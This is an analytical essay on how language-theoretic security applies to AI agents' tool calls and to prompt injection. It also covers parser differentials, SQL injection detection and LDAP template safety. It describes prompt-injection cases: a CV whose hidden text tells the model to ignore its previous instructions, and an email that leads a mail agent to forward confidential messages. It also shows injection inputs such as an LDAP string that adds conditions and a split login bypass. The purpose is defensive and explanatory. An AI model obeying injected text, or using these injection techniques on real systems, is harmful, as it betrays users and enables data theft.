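# Language-theoretic security applied to the tool interfaces of AI agents and to prompt injection

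## How agents read text and call tools, and what prompt injection is

Language-theoretic security, or LangSec, is a school of computer security that treats every program input as a string in a formal language, which is an exactly defined set of strings. Under this approach, a program should check the whole input against that definition before using any of it. LangSec researchers have mostly studied inputs meant for machines, and the parsers and compilers that process them. In an AI agent, a large language model chooses actions and other software carries them out. The agent takes in emails, web pages and documents in ordinary prose, which arrive in the same stream as its instructions. Prompt injection exploits this mixture by using text from an untrusted source to make the model depart from the task that its developer or user set. In 2025, von Hippel and Miyazono argued in *Research Report*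 that the security of systems built on language models is "inherently, a language-theoretic problem". Judging that claim requires some knowledge of how agents handle text and of what formal language theory can and cannot decide.

### Tokens and the context window

A language model works on tokens, which are short pieces of text, often a word or part of a word. A token is roughly three-quarters of an English word (Anthropic's *Introducing 100K Context Windows*, 2023, equates 100,000 tokens with around 75,000 words). Given a sequence of tokens, the model computes how likely each possible token is to come next. The software around it picks one, appends it to the sequence and runs the model again, until the output is complete.

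The sequence has a maximum length, the context window. Anthropic's *Context windows* calls it a "working memory", as opposed to the much larger body of text used in training. The window holds everything the model can refer to while it generates a response, including the response so far. The model keeps nothing between requests, so each request in a conversation has to include the earlier messages along with the new one. The window usually contains a system prompt, the developer's standing instructions, before the user types anything.

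### The agent loop

A model on its own only produces text. To make it useful for, say, office work, a developer gives it tools, which are functions that the developer's software can run when the model asks. Take a mail assistant with three of them:

- `read_inbox` returns the user's recent messages.
- `send_email(to, subject, body)` sends a message from the user's account.
- `create_event(date, start, attendees)` puts a meeting in the calendar.

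Suppose the user asks the assistant to answer Dana's email about meeting on Thursday. Anthropic's *How tool use works* sets out the loop that follows in five steps, which for the mail assistant come to this:

1. The application sends the model the user's request together with descriptions of the three tools.
2. The model's output is a tool call, a structured message that names a function and its arguments. Here it names `read_inbox`.
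3. The application runs the function and collects the text of the messages.
4. The application sends a new request. It contains the original request, the model's tool call and the contents of the inbox.
5. With Dana's email now in the context window, the model emits another call, perhaps to `create_event` and then to `send_email`. The cycle repeats until the model returns an answer with no tool call in it.

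The model never runs anything itself. Each tool call is a request, and ordinary code must act on it before it has any effect. Tools that the model's provider hosts, such as web search, are a partial exception. Anthropic runs these on its own servers, and a model may search, read the results and search again several times before the developer's application receives anything.

The call that answers Dana might look like this in JSON, a text format for nested lists and named values:

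```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "input": {
    "to": "dana@example.com",
    "subject": "Thursday",
    "body": "Two o'clock suits me. See you then."
  }
}
```

Behind it stands a schema, a declaration of the fields, types and allowed values of the message:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "description": "Send an email from the user's account.",
  "input_schema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
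      "to": {"type": "string", "description": "Recipient's address"},
      "subject": {"type": "string"},
      "body": {"type": "string"}
    },
    "required": ["to", "subject", "body"],
    "additionalProperties": false
  }
}
```

This schema requires three string fields and forbids any others. Schemas can be tighter. In OpenAI's *Function calling* guide, for example, a weather tool's `units` field accepts only "celsius" or "fahrenheit", and the schema for `create_event` could similarly require `attendees` to be a list. According to the guide, a model's conformity to the schema may be only "best effort" by default, but developers can turn on a strict mode for closer conformity. The general technique for guaranteeing conformity is constrained decoding, which blocks every token that would take the output outside a given grammar.

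A tool call can fit its schema and still contain a value the user never gave. Anthropic's *Tool use with Claude* warns that if a user asks about the weather without naming a place, some models may guess a value for the required `location` field, such as New York.

Tool descriptions also reach the model as text. OpenAI inserts them into the system message, where they count as input tokens. The Model Context Protocol is a common standard for servers that offer tools to models. Under this standard, each tool has a unique name and metadata describing its schema (Model Context Protocol, *Tools*, 2026). When a developer connects the mail assistant to someone else's server, that server's tool descriptions therefore enter the context window.

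A tool call has a schema, but its result need not have any fixed form. OpenAI recommends returning a string in whatever format the developer likes, which the model will then "interpret" as needed. In Anthropic's format, the application puts the result inside a message with the user's role. A label marks the block as a tool result, but if the tool reads email, the text in the block might come from anyone who has the user's email address.

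*The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) sorts an agent's inputs by how far the agent should trust them. The system prompt and the user's request are trusted, while tool results are untrusted because the agent's operator does not fully control the environment they come from. Documents from a reference database and the training data fall somewhere in between. A conventional program can receive such inputs through separate interfaces, but an agent holds them all in one context memory, with textual separators between them.

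Agents of this sort were already common by early 2025. Von Hippel and Miyazono asked Maitai, a company that hosts and routes language models, to analyze its customers' traffic. About 32.7% of requests involved tool calls, and about another 21.2% involved structured outputs, where the model's answer must conform to a schema but no tool is called. These figures come from one company and are now rather old.

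### Prompt injection

David C, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, dates the term to 2022 and illustrates it with a system for recruiters. The developer's instruction tells the model to score whether a CV meets the job's requirements, and the application then adds each candidate's CV to the prompt. One candidate has put hidden text in the CV, telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the CV for interview. If the model does so, something the developer meant as data has worked as an instruction. David C puts this down to the way the model operates: it predicts the next token from the text so far, and nothing in that operation separates data from instructions. (For that reason the article doubts that prompt injection will ever have as complete a fix as SQL injection, the older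 attack on databases from which it takes its name.)

The CV is an indirect prompt injection because the candidate has no access to the recruiter's system and only writes something that the system will later process. In direct prompt injection, the attacker is the person typing to the model. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) describes a user who asks a booking assistant for a table and adds that, as part of their dietary preferences, they need a list of the allergies that earlier customers reported. The user may make a booking but has no right to other customers' data.

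Definitions of direct and indirect prompt injection vary slightly. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues report that the distinction depends on who the attacker is, but choose not to use it. Wang and colleagues classify attacks by channel, so malicious user input is direct and instructions embedded in external resources are indirect. These definitions conflict when an honest user copies text from an attacker's website into the prompt, because the attacker is a third party but the text arrives as user input. For most purposes, the attacker's identity seems the more useful test, since it shows whose interests the agent is serving.

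Indirect injection is the greater concern for the mail assistant. In their study of an email and calendar agent, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues point out that the user gains nothing by attacking the assistant, because it has the same access as the user. A stranger could gain a lot, and needs only to send an email or a calendar invitation. The next time the user asks for a summary of the inbox, `read_inbox` returns the stranger's text with the other messages, and a successful injection might lead the model to emit a `send_email` call that forwards confidential messages. It might also alter an action the user did request, for instance by adding private information to a reply. An attacker might also try to delete a message before the user sees it, or ask a colleague in the user's name to approve something.

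Research has moved in the same direction. Of the 37 attack papers that Wang and colleagues collected up to October 2025, 20 dealt with indirect injection, and 30 described attacks meant to make the system do the wrong thing rather than leak data or stall.

People often confuse jailbreaking with prompt injection. In a jailbreak, a user gets a model to produce something its developer trained it to refuse, such as instructions for making a weapon. That content is objectionable whether or not the model is connected to other software. In a prompt injection, the model may do nothing that its developer has forbidden in general. A mail assistant is meant to send email, for example, and the harm comes from its sending a particular email on a stranger's behalf. The two can overlap, as when a user persuades a shop's chatbot to ignore its system prompt and produce forbidden content, or when an attacker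 uses jailbreaking tricks inside an injection. Wang and colleagues treat jailbreaking as a separate topic and left papers about it out of their survey.

### Formal languages and what is decidable about them

The other half of the background is older and has nothing to do with AI. Formal language theory begins with an alphabet, a finite set of symbols. A string is a finite sequence of those symbols, and a language is a set of strings. Most interesting languages are infinite, so nobody can define them by listing their members. A grammar defines them by rules instead. Take these two:

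S → ab

S → aSb

Each rule lets a writer replace S with the string on the rule's right side. Starting from S, the second rule gives aSb, and applying the first rule to the S in the middle gives aabb. The language of this grammar is the set of all strings with one or more a's followed by the same number of b's, such as ab, aabb and aaabbb.

A recognizer is a program that checks whether a string belongs to a given language. A parser also works out the structure that the grammar assigns to the string, typically as a tree. For the tool call above, a recognizer would confirm only that the message is well formed, while a parser would return the recipient, the subject and the body as separate values.

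In 1956 the linguist Noam Chomsky described a hierarchy of grammars based on the form their rules may take, and each class turned out to match a type of abstract machine. The usual hierarchy has four levels, but the table adds a fifth, the deterministic context-free languages, because they matter a lot in practice. Each class in the table includes all the classes above it.

| Class | Example | Machine that recognizes it | Membership | Equivalence |
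|---|---|---|---|---|
| Regular | Four digits, a hyphen, two digits, a hyphen, two digits | Finite automaton, with a fixed number of states and no other memory | Decidable | Decidable |
| Deterministic context-free | Some a's, then equally many b's | Stack machine that never guesses | Decidable | Decidable |
| Context-free | Even-length palindromes, such as abba | Stack machine that may guess | Decidable | Undecidable |
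| Context-sensitive | Some a's, then equally many b's, then equally many c's | Turing machine with memory in proportion to the input | Decidable | Undecidable |
| Recursively enumerable | Descriptions of programs that eventually halt | Turing machine with unlimited memory | Undecidable | Undecidable |

The examples show what each step up the hierarchy makes possible. A finite automaton cannot match a's against b's, because it has a fixed number of states, so two different counts must eventually lead to the same state. A machine with a stack can match them by adding a marker for every a, removing one for every b, and accepting if the stack is empty exactly when the input ends. Palindromes also need a stack, but a machine that reads from left to right cannot tell when it has reached the middle, so it has to guess. A single stack is not enough to match a's, b's and c's, because removing the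 markers to count the b's leaves none to count the c's.

The last two columns concern the membership and equivalence problems. The membership problem is to determine whether a given string belongs to the language a given grammar defines. The equivalence problem is to determine whether two grammars, such as those behind two programs that read the same file format, define the same language. A problem is decidable if a single procedure finishes with the right answer for every instance.

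Membership is decidable for all but the last class. In that class, for example, a computer can confirm that a program halts by running it until it stops, but a program that is still running after a year may yet halt or may run forever. Where membership is decidable, the time needed to decide it varies. Parsing a deterministic context-free language takes time proportional to the length of the input, whereas the standard general methods for context-free languages can take time proportional to the cube of that length.

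Equivalence becomes undecidable much earlier, between the deterministic context-free languages and the context-free languages in general. Proving that it is decidable for the deterministic languages was hard, and Géraud Sénizergues won the 2002 Gödel Prize for it. No method can decide equivalence for every pair of context-free grammars, but many particular pairs are easy to settle. A computer can always detect that two grammars differ by testing every string in order of length until it finds one that only one of them generates, but this search never ends if the grammars are equivalent.

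JSON allows brackets to nest to any depth, so recognizing it requires a stack, and a deterministic pushdown automaton is enough. The schema for a `send_email` call fixes the fields and rules out unlimited nesting, so the valid calls form a regular language. The permitted values of the `body` field also form a regular language, but it contains every possible string, so its recognizer accepts every input.

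## The LangSec argument, premise by premise

Some protocols and file formats seem to produce new security holes forever, however often programmers patch them. Sassaman, Patterson and colleagues (2011), in *Security Applications of Formal Language Theory*, proposed an explanation: the design of these formats forces programmers to attempt problems that no program can solve. Their argument has four steps:

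1. Handling an input means running a program that the sender wrote.
2. A component is safe only if it rejects every input outside the language its designer intended.
3. For the most powerful class of languages, no procedure can always decide whether an input belongs. For a much wider range of classes, no procedure can always decide whether two parsers agree.
4. Designers should therefore choose the weakest language that does the job, and programs should recognize an input completely before acting on any of it.

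Steps 1 to 3 are premises, and step 4 is the advice that Sassaman and colleagues draw from them. The argument has changed little since. In their call for papers for the twelfth LangSec workshop, the organisers still describe any software that processes inputs as an interpreter, and the inputs as its programs (LangSec, 2026).

### Input as a program

A computer that receives a message decodes it and then does further work that depends on the result. Sassaman and colleagues therefore treat sending a message as requesting a computation. On this view, even a thermostat with two buttons interprets a small programming language, with one instruction for warmer and one for cooler, and anyone who presses the buttons is writing a program in that language.

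Stated this broadly, the premise is true of all software, so it can't separate safe programs from unsafe ones. The thermostat's users can only bring it into states its designer planned. The danger arises when crafted input takes a program outside its planned states and continues to control it there. Exploit developers call the unintended computer this gives an attacker a weird machine, and Sassaman and colleagues adopted the term. Dullien (2017), in *Weird machines, exploitability, and provable unexploitability*, complains that LangSec authors use the term vaguely and with varying meanings, and supplies a definition.

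Dullien starts from the finite-state machine that the developer meant to build, which the real program imitates on a general-purpose computer. Some of the computer's states represent an intended state or a harmless transition between two intended states. All others are weird states. A program in a weird state often keeps running, applying its ordinary operations to data that its author never planned for. This creates a weird machine, with the attacker's inputs as its instructions. An exploit is a program for the weird machine that breaks a security property of the intended machine.

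The paper works this through for a small server that stores up to 5,000 pairs of a password and a secret. The server releases each secret once, to whoever sends its password, and is secure if an attacker can do no better than guess. Dullien writes one version that keeps the pairs in a plain array and a faster one that uses linked lists, in which each entry holds the memory address of the next. Dullien then lets the attacker stop the program at any moment, flip one bit of its memory (outside a few protected registers) and resume it.

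One flipped bit in an address is enough to defeat the linked-list version. The server starts reading in the wrong place, treats a stored secret as a password, and ends up overwriting the defender's password with a number the attacker can predict. Dullien proves that the same flip gains the attacker essentially nothing against the array version, because an attacker without it could do as well by sending at most 10,000 extra requests.

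This result is awkward for LangSec in two ways. Both versions of the server accept exactly the same very simple input language, pairs of 32-bit numbers, so the language can't explain why only one version is exploitable. Every request in the successful attack is also valid, so a perfect recognizer would have accepted them all. LangSec's defenders can fairly reply that the attack began with a memory fault, not an input. Dullien thinks the most common source of weird states in practice is human error in writing the program, and bad input triggers many such errors. Recognition probably blocks the most common way into the weird machine, but it doesn't block the others or limit what an attacker can do once inside.

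Dullien's definition also requires us to specify the intended machine, and which of its properties matter for security, before we can identify which states are weird. The looser usage makes this requirement easy to miss.

### Recognizing before acting

Sassaman and colleagues want the recognizer in front of a program to be sound (it accepts only strings in the language), complete (it accepts all of them), and guaranteed to finish. Many programs have no such recognizer, and their input checks are scattered through the code that processes the input. LangSec researchers call this shotgun parsing.

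Suppose a warehouse program reads an order line by line. It reads the quantity, checks that it is a positive number and deducts it from the stock. Then it reads the delivery address, finds it malformed and stops. Every check worked, but the stock count is now wrong, because the program acted on part of an input that it should have rejected as a whole. LangSec's slogan for preventing this is "Full Recognition Before Processing!"

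Adding more checks doesn't necessarily help. Sassaman, Patterson and Bratus (2012) write in *A Patch for Postel's Robustness Principle* that a programmer at any given point in the code knows the data needs checking but often can't see what earlier code has already established. An auditor reading the program later has the same difficulty. Checking everything again in every function would solve this but slow the program down, which puts developers off. At LangSec's 2026 workshop, Brady and Smith presented an analysis that finds the fewest places where a program needs a parser. In their analysis, a value that passes through a function unchanged keeps its status, and only modified values need a new check.

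The demand for strict recognition conflicts with one of the oldest rules of internet engineering. In 1980 Jon Postel wrote in his specification of TCP, the protocol that carries most internet traffic, that programs should be conservative in what they send and liberal in what they receive. The rule let programs by different authors work together despite small mistakes. Sassaman, Patterson and Bratus think that later programmers took it too far. The 1980 text limits tolerance to technical errors that leave the meaning clear, and a 1989 restatement adds that implementers should assume the network is full of malevolent senders.

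Whether a faulty message has a clear meaning depends on which other messages the protocol allows, since a receiver could confuse it with one of those. Clarity is therefore a property of the whole protocol, and the article argues that only protocols that are easy to parse have it. For example, if a length field, which states how many bytes the next item occupies, is damaged, the receiver will probably misread everything after it. An unknown value in a fixed-length error code does not cause this problem, so the article would allow software to tolerate a fifth code where the specification lists four.

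LangSec's revision of Postel's rule begins "Be definite about what you accept." Under the rest of the rule, programmers should generate the recognizer from a grammar, match its computing power to the input language, and treat computing power in input handling as a privilege, reducing it where they can.

A definite specification can still accept a wide range of input. If a program has to support a faulty client, *The Seven Turrets of Babel* (Momot, Bratus and colleagues, 2016) advises changing the specification to include that client's messages. This answers the objection that many programs handle malformed input safely. But it also makes premise 2 nearly true by definition, because anything a program can safely tolerate can become part of the intended language. The remaining requirement is that someone write the language down and that the program enforce it.

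### What can't be decided

Few formats fall, by syntax alone, into the one class of languages where membership is undecidable. Sassaman and colleagues call the combination of HTML5 and CSS3, the languages of web pages, an undecidable input language because, they say, a page can carry out arbitrary computation. But that computation happens when a browser displays the page, and a program can still check whether the page is well formed.

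*Seventy Years of Parsing*, a paper by Lucas, Anantharaman and Smith for the 2026 workshop, distinguishes valid syntax from good behaviour. A PDF file may contain JavaScript. Checking the syntax of that code is tractable, but if a PDF is valid only when its code runs without error, no program can check validity in every case. Undecidability is therefore mostly a problem for designers who count good behaviour as part of validity.

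The theory seems to apply more often to comparing two parsers, because equivalence becomes undecidable just above the deterministic context-free languages. In drawing this line, the 2011 report mistakenly states that "All unambiguous context-free grammars are deterministic", where an unambiguous grammar is one that gives no string two different parse trees. Every deterministic grammar is unambiguous, but the reverse does not hold. For example, even-length palindromes have an unambiguous grammar (S → aSa, S → bSb, and a rule that replaces S with nothing), but no stack machine can recognize them without guessing. According to *Why the equivalence problem for unambiguous grammars has not been solved* (2022), most unambiguous grammars are not deterministic.

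The slip matters because Sénizergues's proof that equivalence is decidable covers only the deterministic languages. *Multiplicity Problems on Algebraic Series and Context-Free Grammars* (2023) still lists decidability for unambiguous grammars in general as an open problem. A designer who has removed every ambiguity from a format therefore can't infer that a procedure exists for deciding whether its parsers are equivalent. LangSec's advice still holds, because it specifically recommends the deterministic class.

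The right requirement for a filter in front of a program may also be containment rather than equivalence. The filter doesn't have to accept the same language as the program, as long as it lets nothing through that lies outside the intended language. According to the 2011 report, containment is undecidable even for deterministic context-free languages, but it is decidable for some smaller classes, such as the visibly pushdown languages. In a visibly pushdown language, each symbol by itself determines whether the parser adds to its stack, removes something from it or leaves it alone. Lucas and colleagues place JSON, the format of tool calls, in this class. They also report that the class is closed under intersection and complement (for languages that sort their symbols in the same way) and that emptiness is decidable. A computer can therefore check that language A lies inside language B by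 constructing the set of strings that are in A but not in B and testing whether it is empty.

Sassaman and colleagues' claim that no good-enough engineering solution exists for an undecidable problem seems too strong, because many pairs of grammars are easy to compare and a cautious program can refuse any input that it can't classify. Lucas and colleagues add that most practical formats are, strictly speaking, finite languages, because their length fields and other limits cap the size of a message. Every question about a finite language can in principle be decided with a lookup table, though the table might need more entries than there are atoms in the universe. Decidability doesn't guarantee a practical solution, either. Momot and colleagues concede that software developers could hardly use Sénizergues's procedure to compare their parsers, and recommend generating parsers from one grammar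 instead. The decidability premise is most useful as a warning about which designs will be hard to reason about.

### One certificate, two names

Two programs that read the same input differently form a parser differential. The best-known example in the LangSec literature concerns X.509, the standard format for the certificates with which websites prove their identity. A certificate authority checks who controls a website's name and then signs a certificate for it. The attack that Sassaman and colleagues describe goes as follows:

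1. The attacker controls an ordinary domain and asks an authority to certify a name under it. The name begins with the address of PayPal's website, continues with a null character (a byte with the value zero) and ends with the attacker's own domain.
2. The authority's software reads the name as a string of known length, in which a null is a character like any other. The result is a peculiar name that belongs to the attacker's domain.
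3. The attacker does control that domain, so the authority signs the certificate.
4. A victim's browser connects to the attacker's server, which presents the certificate. No byte of it has changed, so the signature is valid.
5. The browser reads the name by the convention of the C programming language, in which a null marks the end of a string. It stops reading after PayPal's address.
6. The browser accepts the attacker's server as PayPal's.

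In the report's notation, M is the name the authority approved, E is the encoding and D is the browser's decoding. The attack works because D(E(M)) ≠ M. It requires no memory corruption, and both ways of reading a string are common. Momot and colleagues say Sassaman and Patterson, working with the security researcher Dan Kaminsky, found more than 20 such differences between the X.509 libraries of the time.

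The case is strong evidence that disagreement between parsers is dangerous, but much weaker evidence that undecidability is to blame, because a finite automaton could have enforced a rule against null characters in names. The two programs agreed that the certificate was acceptable, so to catch the problem, a proof would have had to show that they extracted the same name, not just that they accepted the same language.

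Lucas and colleagues discuss a stricter test of this kind, called structural equivalence, which asks whether two grammars produce the same parse trees. It is decidable for all context-free grammars, although plain equivalence is not. The test would reject two harmless parsers whose grammars differ only in how they arrange the same content. Still, its decidability weakens the claim that parser agreement becomes uncheckable above the deterministic languages. In *A Survey of Parser Differential Anti-Patterns*, Ali and Smith describe a more practical obstacle, the difficulty of extracting the parser from a large program.

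Differentials have continued to appear. An article in ;login: (2020), a magazine for systems engineers, lists then-recent cases in macOS, GitLab and F5's network equipment. At the 2026 workshop, Applegate and Kellas reported 14 new discrepancies among three official readers of pickle, the format in which Python programs save objects, including many machine-learning models. Pickle has no specification, so they had to write their own grammar for it. Four of the discrepancies let a malicious file get past security scanners like those on Hugging Face, a site for sharing models.

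Sassaman and colleagues deliberately exclude from their 2011 theory of parser differentials cases where two receivers decode a message identically but act on it differently, which they call divergent program semantics. For example, two mail programs might both decode a message's priority as "urgent", but only one might then forward it to a manager's phone. Comparing their parsers wouldn't reveal the difference. Two language models can likewise receive identical tokens and do different things with them, so the theory doesn't cover that case.

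### Does language class predict vulnerability?

The advice to choose the weakest sufficient language assumes that stronger languages lead to more vulnerabilities. The most useful evidence comes from Momot and colleagues, who sort LangSec errors into seven types and provide the examples below.

| Error | Example |
|---|---|
| Shotgun parsing | In the web framework Rails, a developer forgot to filter dots from file paths, so requests could reach files in other directories |
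| Input-handling code with more power than it needs | The search engine Elasticsearch accepted query scripts in a general-purpose language, and attackers could run their own code |
| Input language beyond deterministic context-free | Image data could move Adobe Reader's writing position outside the memory set aside for the picture |
| Differing interpretations of the input language | Android's signature checker and its installer found different contents in the same package |
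| Incomplete specification | An old protocol in the OpenSSL library allowed part of a key to travel unencrypted, and its specification hardly said when this was permissible |
| Overloaded field | In the time protocol NTP, a field that identified a key could also mean "authentication not required" |
| Permissive processing of invalid input | In the Heartbleed flaw, OpenSSL answered requests that were shorter than they claimed to be |

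Momot and colleagues then reviewed all 47 vulnerabilities recorded in OpenSSL, a widely used cryptography library, from January 2015 to June 2016. They judged that 35 of them, or about 74%, would not have occurred if the library's design had avoided the seven errors. They attributed 13 to shotgun parsing and 11 to the processing of invalid input. The 12 vulnerabilities that LangSec would not have prevented mostly involved cryptography or the timing of parallel operations. None of the 47 came from an input language beyond the deterministic context-free class.

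These are judgments by LangSec advocates about what would have happened under a different design, and another reader might classify the cases differently. Heartbleed, which predates the survey, involved a false length field, so it could equally be classified as a problem of language complexity. Even so, the survey supports LangSec's advice about separate and strict validation much better than its advice about language classes. OpenSSL could easily have had bugs caused by complex languages, since it reads certificates in ASN.1, a format that Lucas and colleagues place outside the context-free languages.

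Parsers for simple languages have also had serious flaws. The web server Nginx reads requests with a hand-written finite automaton, the weakest type of machine in the hierarchy. Programmers took more than ten years to find an overflow in it that closely resembled one already well understood in the Apache server. Momot and colleagues blame the layout of the code, which mixed the states for all parts of the grammar in 57 branching statements.

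The PKCS#1 format for digital signatures is another simple language, although Sassaman and colleagues use it as an example of a context-sensitive one. In 2006, Daniel Bleichenbacher showed how to forge signatures that some programs accepted because they checked the padding around the signed data badly. Sassaman and colleagues' report offers a proof that the format is not context-free, but the proof assumes a fixed key size. A fixed size allows only finitely many padded blocks, so the format is regular, as every finite language is.

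The Chomsky hierarchy is also a poor guide to how hard a format is to parse. Length fields take a format out of the context-free class, but Lucas and colleagues describe a class from 2017, the calc-regular languages, that includes length fields and can be parsed in linear time, faster than the standard general methods for context-free languages. LangSec researchers don't always agree on which formats pass their test. Momot and colleagues recommend Protocol Buffers, Google's format for structured data, as one that can stay within the deterministic context-free class if designers avoid complex internal dependencies. Lucas and colleagues place it outside the context-free languages, and conclude that the hierarchy doesn't accurately capture the formats people design.

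A proper test would compare the rate of vulnerabilities across formats of different classes, allowing for their age, their size and how much attention they get from attackers. Neither Sassaman and colleagues nor Momot and colleagues attempt this. Ali, Anantharaman and colleagues (2021), in *What We Have Here Is Failure to Validate*, sort a wave of exploits from the summer of 2020 by root cause, but a collection of exploited systems can't show how they differ from systems that nobody exploited. Complicated languages may plausibly lead to more mistakes, because people find them harder to specify and check, but there is little evidence that the danger rises sharply at the boundary of the deterministic context-free languages.

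LangSec researchers have nevertheless begun to apply the rule to AI agents. At the 2026 workshop, O'Connor presented CBCL, a language for messages between agents that stays within the deterministic context-free class even when agents define new vocabulary for each other. Machine-checked proofs show that these definitions can't expand without limit, respect declared resource limits and leave the core vocabulary intact. These restrictions should make the messages easy to parse, and they limit the computation a sender can demand from the parser, but they don't limit the harm a correctly parsed message can do. Sassaman and colleagues call computing power a form of privilege, but an order to delete a database needs hardly any computing power, and a language containing only that order is regular.

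## Injection as a separate kind of input flaw

If a program puts a stranger's text into a database command, the database may delete its records without malfunctioning. It parses a well-formed command correctly and carries it out, so the fault lies in the program that built the command. In *LangSec revisited* (2018), Poll observed that nearly all the research at LangSec's annual workshop dealt with buggy parsers, and argued that even perfect parsers would not eliminate such faults.

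### Processing flaws and forwarding flaws

Poll divides input flaws into two categories. In a processing flaw, the program that reads the input handles it wrongly, as when a PDF viewer writes past the end of a buffer. Parser differentials are also processing flaws. In a forwarding flaw, a front end passes untrusted input to a back end, which correctly parses it as something the front end's designer never meant to send. The standard example is SQL injection, where the front end is a web application, the back end is a database, and the two communicate in SQL, a language for database queries.

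An attacker who exploits a processing flaw uses behaviour that got into a program by accident, while one who exploits a forwarding flaw uses a feature that somebody built on purpose but exposed by accident. Malicious email attachments can exploit either kind. A crafted PDF may depend on a bug in one particular viewer, whereas a Word document with a macro uses Word's ability to run commands. Poll thinks the macro is often more attractive to attackers because it is easier to write and needs no bug.

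The idea of a weird machine therefore explains little about injection. Alata and Gimenez point out in *Towards programming languages free of injection-based vulnerabilities by design* (2025) that the database and the application may both stay in their intended states throughout an attack. A SQL recognizer in front of the database wouldn't help, because the attacker's query is valid SQL. Sassaman and colleagues describe such a query as valid for the database in isolation but invalid given the database's role in the application. The language that needs enforcing is much smaller than SQL, and usually nobody has written it down.

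Some injections involve no forwarding. Telephone networks once carried control tones on the same line as callers' voices, so a caller could control the network by imitating the tones with a device called a blue box. Poll classes such attacks on in-band signalling as injection without forwarding, because the caller had direct access to the interface, with no front end in between.

*Secure Input Handling* (Poll, 2024) explains why cleaning input as it arrives, the usual first response to a forwarding flaw, tends to go wrong. An application can't refuse quotation marks, which have a special meaning in SQL, because the Dutch town of 's-Hertogenbosch has one in its name. It can escape them by adding characters that make the back end read them literally. But SQL, web pages and file names all need different escaping, and the program may not yet know where the text will end up. PHP, a programming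 language for websites, had a feature called magic quotes that escaped all incoming data automatically, but PHP's developers removed it in 2012. Escaping on output works better, since by then the program knows the destination.

### The case against strings

Poll (2018), in *Strings Considered Harmful*, blames injection flaws on the more basic habit of passing strings between components at all. A string might hold a user name, a web address or a piece of JavaScript, and its type doesn't indicate which, or whether anyone has checked it. It is also unparsed by definition, so some later component has to parse it, and that may not be the component the programmer intended. An interface that accepts a string often accepts a whole language. For example, a function that takes an SQL query as a string accepts any SQL query, including one that deletes tables.

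Programmers make the problem worse when they build queries by concatenating their own text with the user's. Poll calls this a form of unparsing. The programmer knew which part was the command and which was the name, but the joined string no longer records this, so the back end has to work out the structure again.

One remedy is a less expressive interface, which lets the front end supply values but not commands. Another is to give each language its own type. If HTML and user names have different types, the compiler can report an error when a programmer puts a user name into a web page without converting it first. Types can also record trust. For example, they can separate constants in the program's source code from outside text, so that sensitive operations accept only the constants. Google's `SafeHtml` type combines these two uses of types. It holds text that a browser can display without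 running an untrusted script, and only a limited set of functions can produce a value of that type.

These protections weaken when data leaves the program for another system, because the data usually has to become a string again, which makes parsing bugs possible again. Some applications also have to make exceptions, such as letting an administrator write a welcome message in raw HTML. Poll's lecture notes recommend an explicit conversion function for such cases, so that reviewers can find every exception with a simple search.

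### Injection as a changed parse tree

Poll's account depends on what the designer intended, which a computer can't check directly. In *The Essence of Command Injection Attacks in Web Applications* (2006), Su and Wassermann replace this intention with a property of the query's parse tree.

Their example is a shop's web page that lists a customer's saved credit cards of a chosen type. The programmer has escaped the quotation marks in both inputs, the customer's name and the card type. But the card type is a number, so the query has no quotation marks around it and the attacker doesn't need one to break out of the input. The attacker sends a number followed by OR and a comparison that is always true, and the page lists every card number in the database.

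In an ordinary request, the card type is a single number with its own node in the tree. In the attack, the input is a number, the word OR and a second comparison. No node has exactly these as its leaves, because SQL groups the number with the conditions to its left before it applies the OR.

Su and Wassermann use this difference to define an injection attack. Let *U* be the set of grammar symbols that the application's policy permits users to supply. An input is acceptable if some node in the query's parse tree is labeled with a symbol from *U* and has exactly that input as its leaves. A query is an injection attack if it parses as SQL and contains at least one input that is not acceptable.

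Their tool, SQLCheck, enforces the definition as follows:

1. It puts a pair of markers around each input, and the markers stay with the text as the application builds the query.
2. For each symbol *u* in *U*, the tool's grammar has an extra symbol that can become either *u* or *u* between markers. This new symbol replaces *u* wherever *u* occurred on the right side of a rule.
3. SQLCheck tries to parse the marked query with this grammar. If it succeeds, it removes the markers and sends the query to the database. Otherwise it blocks the query.

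Su and Wassermann prove that this procedure lets through exactly the valid SQL queries that are not attacks under their definition. They also tested it on five web applications, each written in two programming languages. SQLCheck blocked all 36,848 attempted attacks and allowed all 7,648 legitimate queries, taking about three milliseconds to check each one.

The attacks came from published exploits that another research group had collected, so none targeted SQLCheck itself. Su and Wassermann concede that an attacker might get past SQLCheck by guessing the markers, which were random four-letter strings in the same text as the data. They propose escaping any marker that appears in an input.

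The proof also doesn't establish whether *U* is a sensible policy. Bugzilla, a program for tracking software bugs, lets users store search conditions and run them later. A condition that is always true is harmless there because it only lists more bugs, but on the shop's page it exposes every customer's card. The parse tree shows the input's role, but a person has to decide which roles are acceptable.

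### Templates and intents

SQLCheck examines one finished query at a time. Alata and Gimenez ask whether a developer could know in advance that no input will cause trouble. They describe a query with one blank as a template (*p*, *s*), where *p* is the developer's text before the blank and *s* is the text after it. If *L* is the back end's language, the inputs that produce a valid query are

*F* = {*w* : *pws* is in *L*}

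Alata and Gimenez represent the developer's intent by a symbol, or a sequence of symbols, of the back end's grammar. Let *E* be the set of strings that the grammar can derive from the intent, and *F* the set of strings that fit the blank. The template is intent-equivalent, and therefore safe, if the grammar permits the intended symbol or sequence in the blank and *F* = *E*.

They illustrate this with LDAP, a language for searching directories of users. A simplified grammar has six rules:

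S → (s=s)

S → (!S)

S → (&L)

S → (|L)

L → S

L → LS

Here s stands for any alphanumeric string, and the signs !, & and | mean "not", "and" and "or". Suppose a developer writes this template, with a blank for the user name:

`(&(uid=____)(passwd=1234))`

1. The developer expects a name, so the intent is s, and *E* contains only alphanumeric strings.
2. A user enters `foo)(loc=bar`.
3. The complete query is `(&(uid=foo)(loc=bar)(passwd=1234))`.
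4. This is valid, because L can become three conditions as easily as two. The input is therefore in *F*.
5. The input contains brackets, so the grammar can't derive it from s, and it is not in *E*.

*F* and *E* differ, so the template is unsafe. This input does little damage, since an extra condition only narrows the search, but the user now controls the number of conditions.

An attacker can split an injection across the name and password fields of a login form. In Alata and Gimenez's example, the text in the first field opens brackets that the text in the second closes. This puts the password comparison inside a negated condition that is always true, so any password works. Neither text would produce a valid query without the other, and checking each field separately would miss the attack.

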